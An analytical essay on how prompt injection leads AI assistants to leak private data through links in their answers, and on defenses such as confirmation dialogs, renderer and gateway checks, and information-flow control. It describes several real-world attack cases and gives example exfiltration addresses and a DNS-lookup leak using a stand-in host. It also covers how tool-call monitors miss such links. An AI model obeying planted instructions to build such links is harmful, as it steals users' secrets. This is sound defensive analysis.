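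An automatic check blocked 89 percent of the same commands. Anthropic published the comparison to support making that check the default, so it had an interest in the result. The testers also worked in a test environment, not on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful. Still, the fall from 17 to 5 percent within the same study is hard to explain without fatigue.

Claude Code users rejected Claude's plans 39 percent of the time. A plan describes in ordinary words what the agent intends to do, so users can compare it with what they want. They often can't do that with a command. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging or mishandling files, and found that the user's review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the request did not make the effect clear. For example, `python3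 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever code the file contains to run. Users have the same problem when a dialog shows a web address without explaining what it would reveal.

Some software learns from past approvals and stops asking about similar actions. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may come from habit, fatigue or a need to keep working rather than growing trust. If an assistant stopped asking about a site after a user had hurriedly opened five links to it, an attacker who could collect data through that site could then do so without the user's approval.

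Link warnings are probably less frequent than requests to run commands, so people may tire of them more slowly. But nearly all of them will be false alarms. Suppose an employee sees five warnings a week for 50 weeks, and one of the 250 links carries stolen data. An employee who always clicks "open" will be right 249 times and will learn to treat the warning as meaningless.

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) cites a large 2013 field study by Akhawe and Felt as evidence that the effect of a browser warning depends strongly on its design. It also cites a 2010 field experiment by Böhme and Köpsell, which found that people accept consent dialogs without much thought when the dialogs resemble familiar ones.

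However, people may respond differently to link dialogs than to browser warnings. A browser usually warns about a site because it matches a known threat. ChatGPT warns about a link because its crawler has no record of the address, so a link to a document shared with one colleague can also trigger the warning. Users therefore have more reason to ignore ChatGPT's warning. None of these studies measured how often people click links in an assistant's answers, so they cannot show how many users would continue past the dialog.

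### What a better dialog would show

Hossain and colleagues tested how much the content of a dialog matters. In one of their examples, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only the summary totals from invoices. A planted instruction makes the agent copy the detailed rows into a file, and the agent then asks permission to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name looks normal, so the user can see the problem only by connecting the file to the earlier copying.

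Eighty volunteers each judged 12 such requests, half of which broke the user's instructions. Each volunteer saw one of four dialogs:

| What the dialog showed | Approved harmful requests | Approved harmless requests | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Those details, the user's original instruction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
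| The same facts, with the combined consequence stated in words | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

Showing a link's full address is similar to the second row of the table, because the user sees the exact action but not where the data came from. People shown that level of detail still approved 43 percent of the harmful requests.

Most of the improvement came from adding facts. Stating the consequence may have helped further. After statistical adjustment, the last two rows differed by 7.9 percentage points in favor of stating it, but with only 20 people per dialog, the plausible range was from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. Half of the requests were harmful, far more than in normal use, so people at work would probably be less alert than these volunteers.

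Applied to the stolen login code, this approach might produce a dialog like this:

```
You asked for: a summary of the Q3 report
This link would send: 481920
Where that came from: an email from Slack, received at 09:02
Who would receive it: files.example, a site you have not used before
Who wrote the address: the assistant, after reading an email
                       from an outside sender

[Do not open]   [Find another source]   [Open and send]
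```

The user can see from the first three lines, without parsing or decoding anything, that summarizing a report should not require a login code from Slack. The label on the last button also states the consequence of clicking it, while "Open" would describe only what the user wants to happen.

Even when the software cannot decode the data in a link, it could show the user that the assistant wrote the link after reading private email. This would give the user a better reason to hesitate than the word "unverified", though it would not prove theft, because an assistant might legitimately put a meeting's location into a map search.

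The model must not write this dialog, because planted text could make it describe a theft as a routine login. Hossain and colleagues' software keeps its own record of the agent's actions and never relies on the agent's explanation. This matters because an assistant's own account can be incomplete, as when Slack AI's citations left out the attacker's message in the main demonstration.

Hossain and colleagues' monitor can make mistakes too. In a separate test with 120 violations, it detected 107, missed seven and was inconclusive on six. If it missed a violation, the user would see a reassuring dialog. The researchers did not test whether people would notice a wrong summary, and recommend studying that next.

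Users could also make some of these decisions before they see an attacker's link. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) studies rules that people without a software background set once for each kind of consequence, such as spending money, sending something or accessing private information. A rule such as "never put anything from my email into a link" would not depend on how the user responds to a loading error.

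### The dispute over responsibility

Companies have disagreed with researchers about how serious these attacks are, partly because a person has to take the last step:

| Finding | Company's first position | What happened later |
|---|---|---|
| Slack AI puts a private API key in a link, 2024 | The evidence was insufficient, and showing messages from public channels was intended behavior | Slack released a patch the next day |
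| Copilot writes invisible characters, January 2024 | Low severity | Microsoft fixed the full attack by July |
| Hidden text changes what Gemini tells the user, 2025 | It can only result in social engineering | Gemini models still obeyed hidden text in August 2026 |
| SearchLeak steals data through Copilot, 2026 | 6.5 out of 10, partly because it needs a click | Microsoft patched it, and the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5 |

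Only the last two positions depend on what the user does. Slack's reviewers had misunderstood where the secret came from, and Microsoft's low rating covered only the invisible characters, not the full attack. Embrace The Red reports that Rehberger objected the same day, saying the rating would be wrong if the characters were part of a longer attack, and received no reply.

TechRadar's *Google says it won't fix this potentially concerning Gemini security issue* summarizes Google's position as placing responsibility on the end user. Security teams often treat social engineering, which means deceiving people into doing something harmful, as a matter for training instead of a flaw in the product.

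The two SearchLeak scores show how much a click can matter in a formal rating. Security teams commonly use the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which multiplies several factors to estimate how easily an attacker can exploit a flaw. In version 3.1, the factor for user interaction is 0.85 if the attack needs none and 0.62 if it needs some. For a flaw that an outsider can easily exploit over the internet, and that exposes data without altering or disabling anything, the calculation is:

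- **No interaction:** 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 = 3.89 for ease of attack, plus 3.60 for impact, which rounds up to 7.5.
- **Interaction required:** 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62 = 2.84 for ease of attack, plus 3.60 for impact, which rounds up to 6.5.

These results match the two scores Expert Insights reports, so the disagreement over the click could explain the whole difference. Varonis called the flaw critical, but the two scores rate it "high" and "medium", a difference that may affect how quickly a company deals with it.

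CVSS uses the same factor for clicks in the Slack AI and SearchLeak attacks, as if both victims had a chance to prevent the theft. A careful Slack AI user could have seen the stolen key before clicking, but a SearchLeak victim had no stolen data to see.

A company can reasonably rate an attack as less severe if it requires a click, because it will fail against some people and a company with hundreds of reported flaws has to fix the worst first. Any product that displays text can also be used to deceive people, and few would blame an email provider for every fraudulent message it delivers. Vendors warn users that an assistant's answers may be wrong, and Embrace The Red describes those disclaimers as the vendors' response to the risk of manipulated answers.

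The comparison with email fails because an assistant can present an attacker's message as its own. Security Boulevard's *Google Gemini AI Flaw Could Lead to Gmail Compromise, Phishing* (2025) describes an email with invisible instructions that made Gemini add a false security alert to its summary. The alert said that Gemini had detected a compromised Gmail password and gave a phone number to call. The user saw only this warning, which appeared to come from Google's own assistant. vict0ni makes a similar point about hidden text in calendar invitations, describing Gemini as a trusted personal assistant and that trust as the attacker's target.

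In the link attacks, the assistant also builds the link. An ordinary email phisher doesn't know the victim's login code and has to persuade the victim to type it. Here the vendor's software finds the code, copies it into an address and includes the link in an answer the user requested, so the user only has to click. The vendor's system processes the planted text, the search and the finished address, while the user may see only the words "click here to reauthenticate".

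A company can reasonably rank a flaw lower because it requires the user to click a link. It should still fix the flaw, because it can change what its assistant retrieves and displays, while users can't.

### When a confirmation is a real check

Google gives an example of a confirmation that users can judge. A user asks Gemini to delete all their events on a Saturday. Gemini finds three, lists their details and asks for confirmation before deleting them. The user knows which events they wanted to remove, so they can check the list. If planted text had added a fourth event from another day, the user would have a good chance of noticing.

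A link confirmation can work in the same way if it appears before any software has opened the address and shows what data would be sent, where it came from and who would receive it. Confirmations also have to be rare enough that people read them, and users need another way to get the answer. False login requests exploit the fact that people will often choose a suspicious link if the only alternative is to leave their task unfinished.

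ChatGPT's published dialog meets some of these conditions. It appears before the link opens, and OpenAI suggests asking for another source. It would have given some victims of the Slack AI attack a fair chance of noticing the theft, because their API key was readable in the address, but a victim of the Mermaid attack would have seen their emails only as hexadecimal. A user who clicked "open" would have formally consented to sending emails they could not read, and the company could later cite that consent even though the dialog had given the user no practical way to detect the theft.

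## Where a security check could stand between the answer and the click

Several pieces of software handle a link after the model writes it and before the attacker's server receives the request, and any of them could check it. Computer security has an old standard for judging such a check. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, set three requirements for a reference monitor on shared US Air Force computers:

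- Nothing can tamper with it.
- The system invokes it on every access.
- It is small enough for people to analyze and test completely.

Anderson also showed how a real system failed these requirements. On one Honeywell computer, the hardware checked that each program stayed inside its own area of memory, but this check was mostly off while the operating system did work for the program, such as reading a file. Treating the whole operating system as the monitor did not help, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were too many to verify. An assistant that checks only its tool calls has a similar gap, because nothing is checked when the user clicks a link.

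Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, write that complete mediation requires a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. A browser can report that the user clicked a link, but not that the link's address came from instructions in a stranger's email.

### Four places for a check

| Position | Information available | What it can block | Routes around it |
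|---|---|---|---|
| Tool-call layer | The name and arguments of each call, and sometimes where the data came from | Searches, messages and web requests by the assistant | Any link in the answer |
| Renderer, the code that displays the answer | The whole answer, including each link's words and address | A link, before the user can click it | Other displays of the same answer, and link formats it misses |
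| Click handler, code that runs when the user clicks | The exact address, at the moment of the click | An ordinary click | Copying the address into another browser, some menu commands, and link previews |
| Network gateway, which filters an organization's internet traffic | The host name, or the full address if the gateway decrypts traffic | Requests from any browser on the organization's network | Phones on mobile data, other companies' servers, and data hidden in host-name lookups |

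A check on tool calls can meet all three of Anderson's requirements and still miss a link in the assistant's answer. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes ARM, a monitor that is the only connection between the model and its tools. It runs as a separate process, and each of its four layers of fixed rules can refuse a call. But a link in an answer never becomes a tool call, so ARM doesn't check it. *Tether* (2026) criticizes existing agent monitors for assuming that every action is a structured call with a known meaning and an explicit target.

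*Kairos* (2026) moves the monitor to the boundary of the isolated environment where the agent runs. The monitor can then catch actions the agent never declared as tool calls, such as a script opening its own connection. It can also hold an outgoing request while the agent continues with a stand-in reply. The user's browser normally runs on a different machine, so this monitor would not cover the click.

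The renderer is the first place where a check can inspect the finished address as the user will receive it. The check's rule could be short, but it would rely on a Markdown parser and often an HTML sanitizer, which are much harder to verify. EchoLeak got through because the filter and the display parsed links differently. The rule also has to be ordinary code, because untrusted data can override a rule in the prompt. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) adds that a second model as monitor does not fully solve this, because that model still receives text the agent controls.

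A click handler can recheck the address and ask the user to confirm, as a redirect page does. However, the browser does not notify the page when someone chooses "Copy link address" and pastes the result into another browser. To close this gap, the assistant's server could store the real address and give the user a link such as `https://assistant.example/open/7f3a91`. Any browser or link preview that opened this link would reach a confirmation page first, and the login code would stay on the vendor's server until the user agreed. This works only if the answer does not also display the real address as text.

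A gateway covers pasted addresses too, as long as the device uses the organization's network. Because "https" encrypts the path and query string, the gateway has to decrypt the traffic to read them, usually using a certificate installed on the organization's devices. Even then, it has no record of the conversation, so it cannot tell whether `481920` came from it. The model cannot tamper with a gateway, but a product that decrypts and inspects all of a company's traffic is too large to verify completely.

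*The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026) notes that data hidden in host-name lookups gets past many controls that block web requests. If the link leads to `481920.files.example`, the computer first has to look up that host's address. The lookup can carry the login code to the attacker's name server, even if the gateway then blocks the page.

### Labeling the text of an answer

None of these checks can determine where the digits in an address came from unless other software keeps track. Information-flow control tracks this by labeling data with its source and secrecy, and it blocks outputs whose labels break a rule. In an early account of the idea, Saltzer and Schroeder called it "putting strings on information" and described a system, ADEPT, that gave each output file the highest classification of any data used to create it.

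*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system that applies information-flow control to AI agents. FIDES labels each piece of data with who may read it and whether it is trusted. When the agent combines two pieces, only people allowed to read both may read the result, and the result is untrusted if either piece was.

FIDES uses these labels mainly to check tool calls, but the same method could check links. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a public web page about third-quarter results. The page contains a link to the full report and some planted instructions. Following them, the assistant finds Slack's email with the login code 481920. Its summary then contains two links:

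`https://files.example/reports/q3`

`https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920`

The software copied the first address from the page unchanged, and the model built the second using the email.

| Text | Who may read it | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|
| The public page | Anyone | No |
| Slack's email | The user and Slack | No |
| First link | Anyone | No |
| Second link | The user and Slack | No |

Opening a link sends its address to a server, so a link must be clickable only if whoever runs that server is allowed to read everything that went into the address. A rule that considered only the user would permit both links, because the user is allowed to read everything in the answer.

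- **First link: allow.** Anyone may read the address, including the operator of `files.example`.
- **Second link: block.** Only the user and Slack may read it, and `files.example` is neither.

As with the public-URL check, the software doesn't have to recognize the login code, however the attacker encodes it. Requiring trusted addresses would be too strict here because it would also block the first link and most other web citations.

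The first link keeps its public label only because the software copied it. FIDES assumes that anything a model writes may depend on everything the model has read. If the model had retyped the address after reading the email, the link would have the email's label and the rule would block it. The developer also has to know who receives data at each host, which open redirects make difficult.

### When private data only chooses the link

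Suppose the planted text instructs the assistant to show the third-quarter link if the user's email mentions a merger, and `https://files.example/reports/q2` if it does not. Both addresses come unchanged from the public page, so the rule permits either one. But when the user clicks, the attacker learns whether the email mentions a merger.

This is an implicit flow, in which private data affects what the assistant does without appearing in the output. FIDES does not prevent it. Costa and colleagues prove a weaker property called explicit secrecy. Take two mailboxes, d₁ and d₂, that look the same to the attacker because they differ only in private content. If the agent performs the same steps, g, on both, the results must also look the same:

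if d₁ =_L d₂, then g(d₁) =_L g(d₂)

Here =_L means "looks the same to the attacker". Showing the third-quarter link passes this test because the address is the same whichever mailbox the user has. The test does not cover what the attacker learns from which link the agent shows, since a different mailbox would have led it to show the other one.

A stricter system could also label the choice:

| Link in the answer | If labels follow only the address's content | If labels also follow the choice |
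|---|---|---|
| Public address, cited after the model has read private email | Allow | Block |
| Address containing the login code | Block | Block |
| One of two public addresses, depending on the email | Allow | Block |

As the first row shows, an assistant that had read any private email could no longer cite a public page, because the email might have influenced which page it cited. Costa and colleagues reject the stricter guarantee for tool calls for a similar reason.

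In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) measured how much an attacker can learn just from which links an agent opens. Their website offered agents several links on different subjects, recorded which one each agent opened, and then offered narrower choices. With four links, the agent's choice revealed what it was researching in 93.8 percent of the trials that produced a visible request. Repeated choices let the attacker reconstruct the concepts in users' questions with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 would mean finding every concept with no false ones. FIDES and three other defenses each changed the scores by less than 0.03.

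These agents opened links themselves and needed about six probes per question, far more than most users would click. The result still shows that checking an address's content does little against this kind of leak. Liang and colleagues reduced the score to 0.39 by having the agent fetch a fixed amount of material, whatever the private data contained, and then choose from its local copy. An assistant could similarly list both reports every time, though the user's choice between them might reveal something.

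Detecting implicit flows is possible but imprecise. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) compared FIDES with NeuroTaint, a system that traces what influenced an agent's actions. NeuroTaint detected 37 of the 40 cases where data affected the agent's decisions, and FIDES detected 17. In 140 cases where the data had no effect, NeuroTaint raised one false alarm and FIDES raised 94. But NeuroTaint raised a false alarm in all 14 of the other harmless cases, which involved several sources or overlapping topics. A summary that cites several pages about one subject may resemble those cases.

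### What existing systems guard

FIDES normally checks only tool calls, because Costa and colleagues consider replies to the user "inconsequential". They add that developers can check replies too where this assumption is unsuitable, and the final answer already carries the labels needed for this check.

The same system is stricter about messages that the agent sends. In the tests, its confidentiality policy for email and Slack rejected any message containing an untrusted link, unless the agent was in a trusted context when it decided to send the message. This rule was meant to stop data theft over the web. The second link from the example could therefore be blocked in a Slack message but appear in an answer to the user.

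CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues proposed in 2025, separates planning from untrusted data. One model plans without reading the results of tool calls, and a second model, which has no tools, processes those results. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's security policies as applying to tool calls. By that description, CaMeL would check a displayed link only if the application treated displaying an answer as a tool call with its own policy. The paper's own system, Prudentia, builds on FIDES and also checks tool calls.

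Some later systems do control what reaches the user, in different ways:

| System | How it treats text for the user | Effect on the link with the login code |
|---|---|---|
| APPA | Checks whether the recipient may read it | Passes if only the user counts as the recipient |
| The system in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* | Can show the user secrets that it hides from the agent | Could appear in full |
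| FlowSeal | Asks a separate model whether a proposed output reveals protected records | Blocked if the model recognizes the leak |

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) treats a reply as an output to a named recipient, and a reply that fails the check cannot be used to approve its own release. This is close to what a defense against the link attack requires, but the policy would also have to count the operator of `files.example` as a second recipient.

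The system in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) treats the user's screen as a safe destination. Its code may transform secret text only in ways that have no outside effects. Adding a login code to the end of an address has no outside effects, so an agent following planted instructions could produce the link without breaking that rule. If the terminal made the address clickable, the user could then send the login code by clicking it.

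FlowSeal, the system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), gives a separate model only the protected records and the proposed output, and the model returns "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". This check can catch paraphrased data that a search for exact text would miss. It could still miss data in a made-up encoding, and it cannot recognize data conveyed only by an innocent-looking choice between two public links.

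OpenAI comes closest to treating links as guarded outputs in a working product. It looks for combinations of a source, through which an attacker can influence the assistant, and a sink, which is an ability, such as following a link, that becomes dangerous in the wrong context.

### The cost in completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. With its policies on, the number of successful attacks fell from 152 for an undefended agent to zero. The agent also completed fewer ordinary tasks when nobody was attacking it:

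| Tasks | GPT-4o, undefended | GPT-4o with FIDES | o1, undefended | o1 with FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 59.0% | 70.0% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 41.0% | 82.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 52.5% | 96.2% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 47.6% | 87.6% | 54.3% |

Both models are old, and the stronger one lost less in every category. But the policy itself caused some failures. For example, a banking task might ask the agent to pay a bill according to instructions in a file. Reading the file makes the agent's context untrusted, so FIDES blocks the payment no matter how capable the model is.

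Kolluri and colleagues object that such comparisons make the defense look worse than it is, because the protected agent must work without any human approval while the undefended agent acts as if a person had approved everything. Prudentia makes the agent aware of the policies, which let it complete up to 9 percent more tasks without approvals than FIDES did and cut the total number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9.

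Kravchenko and colleagues report a smaller drop in completed tasks with newer models. On 20 simulated corporate tasks, APPA completed 88 to 90 percent of attempts, and none of the 600 attempts led to a successful attack. Agents with permissive policies completed 90 to 92.5 percent, but attacks succeeded in 30 to 39.5 percent of attempts. The researchers designed both the tasks and the policies, so the drop might be larger at other companies.

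Guarding replies to the user left more tasks unfinished. On tasks involving false or malicious entries in the agent's memory, APPA completed 71 of 150, while a FIDES configuration that did not check the path from memory to the user completed all 150. When the prompt encouraged agents to follow embedded instructions, that configuration let through 103 of 150 attacks. These attacks were not about links. A rule that removed only suspicious links would probably prevent fewer tasks from being completed, but none of these experiments measured its effect on task completion.

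### Whether a click authorizes the release

A rule that blocks every address built from private data would also block useful links, such as a map search for the place named in a calendar entry. The software could instead treat the user's click as permission to send the data.

There is a good case for treating the user's click as consent to send the data. Saltzer and Schroeder define privacy as a person's ability to decide whether, when and to whom to release information, and the login code belongs to the user. Costa and colleagues allow a related exception, in which an agent may send private data if it decided to do so in a trusted context. The user is trusted, and planted text cannot click a link. Microsoft also relies on explicit consent where its other defenses are insufficient. For example, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to approve the text and send it.

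The comparison with Outlook also shows what is wrong with the argument. Someone sending an email can read the message and check the recipient, but someone who clicks "Q3 report" has agreed to open a report and may not know that the address contains a login code.

The basic rule in FIDES for actions with consequences requires both the decision to act and every detail of the action to be trusted. A click on a link fails this rule when the address comes from a stranger's instructions, even if the user decided to click. For its tests, FIDES used a looser rule that checked only the decision, and the same click would pass. Treating any click as authorization amounts to choosing the looser rule, which doesn't check the address even though the attacker controls it.

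Before an untrusted address opens, a dialog can show the user the data to be sent, its source and its recipient, and ask for approval. Only this approval, not the first click, authorizes opening the address. The check would still be imperfect, since people approved some harmful requests even with the best dialog that Hossain and colleagues tested.

The permission should also cover only one exact web address. APPA ties each approval to a single action in its final form, so the agent cannot reuse the approval or change the action afterward. Kolluri and colleagues similarly chose not to let users declare private data safe to release in general, because whether a release is appropriate depends on the situation. For example, a user who approves a map search for a meeting has not agreed to send the meeting's location to every site the assistant links to later.

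For the merger links, a user could not give informed permission even if a dialog described the address accurately. Software that tracked only the address's content could not show the user that a different email would have produced a different link.
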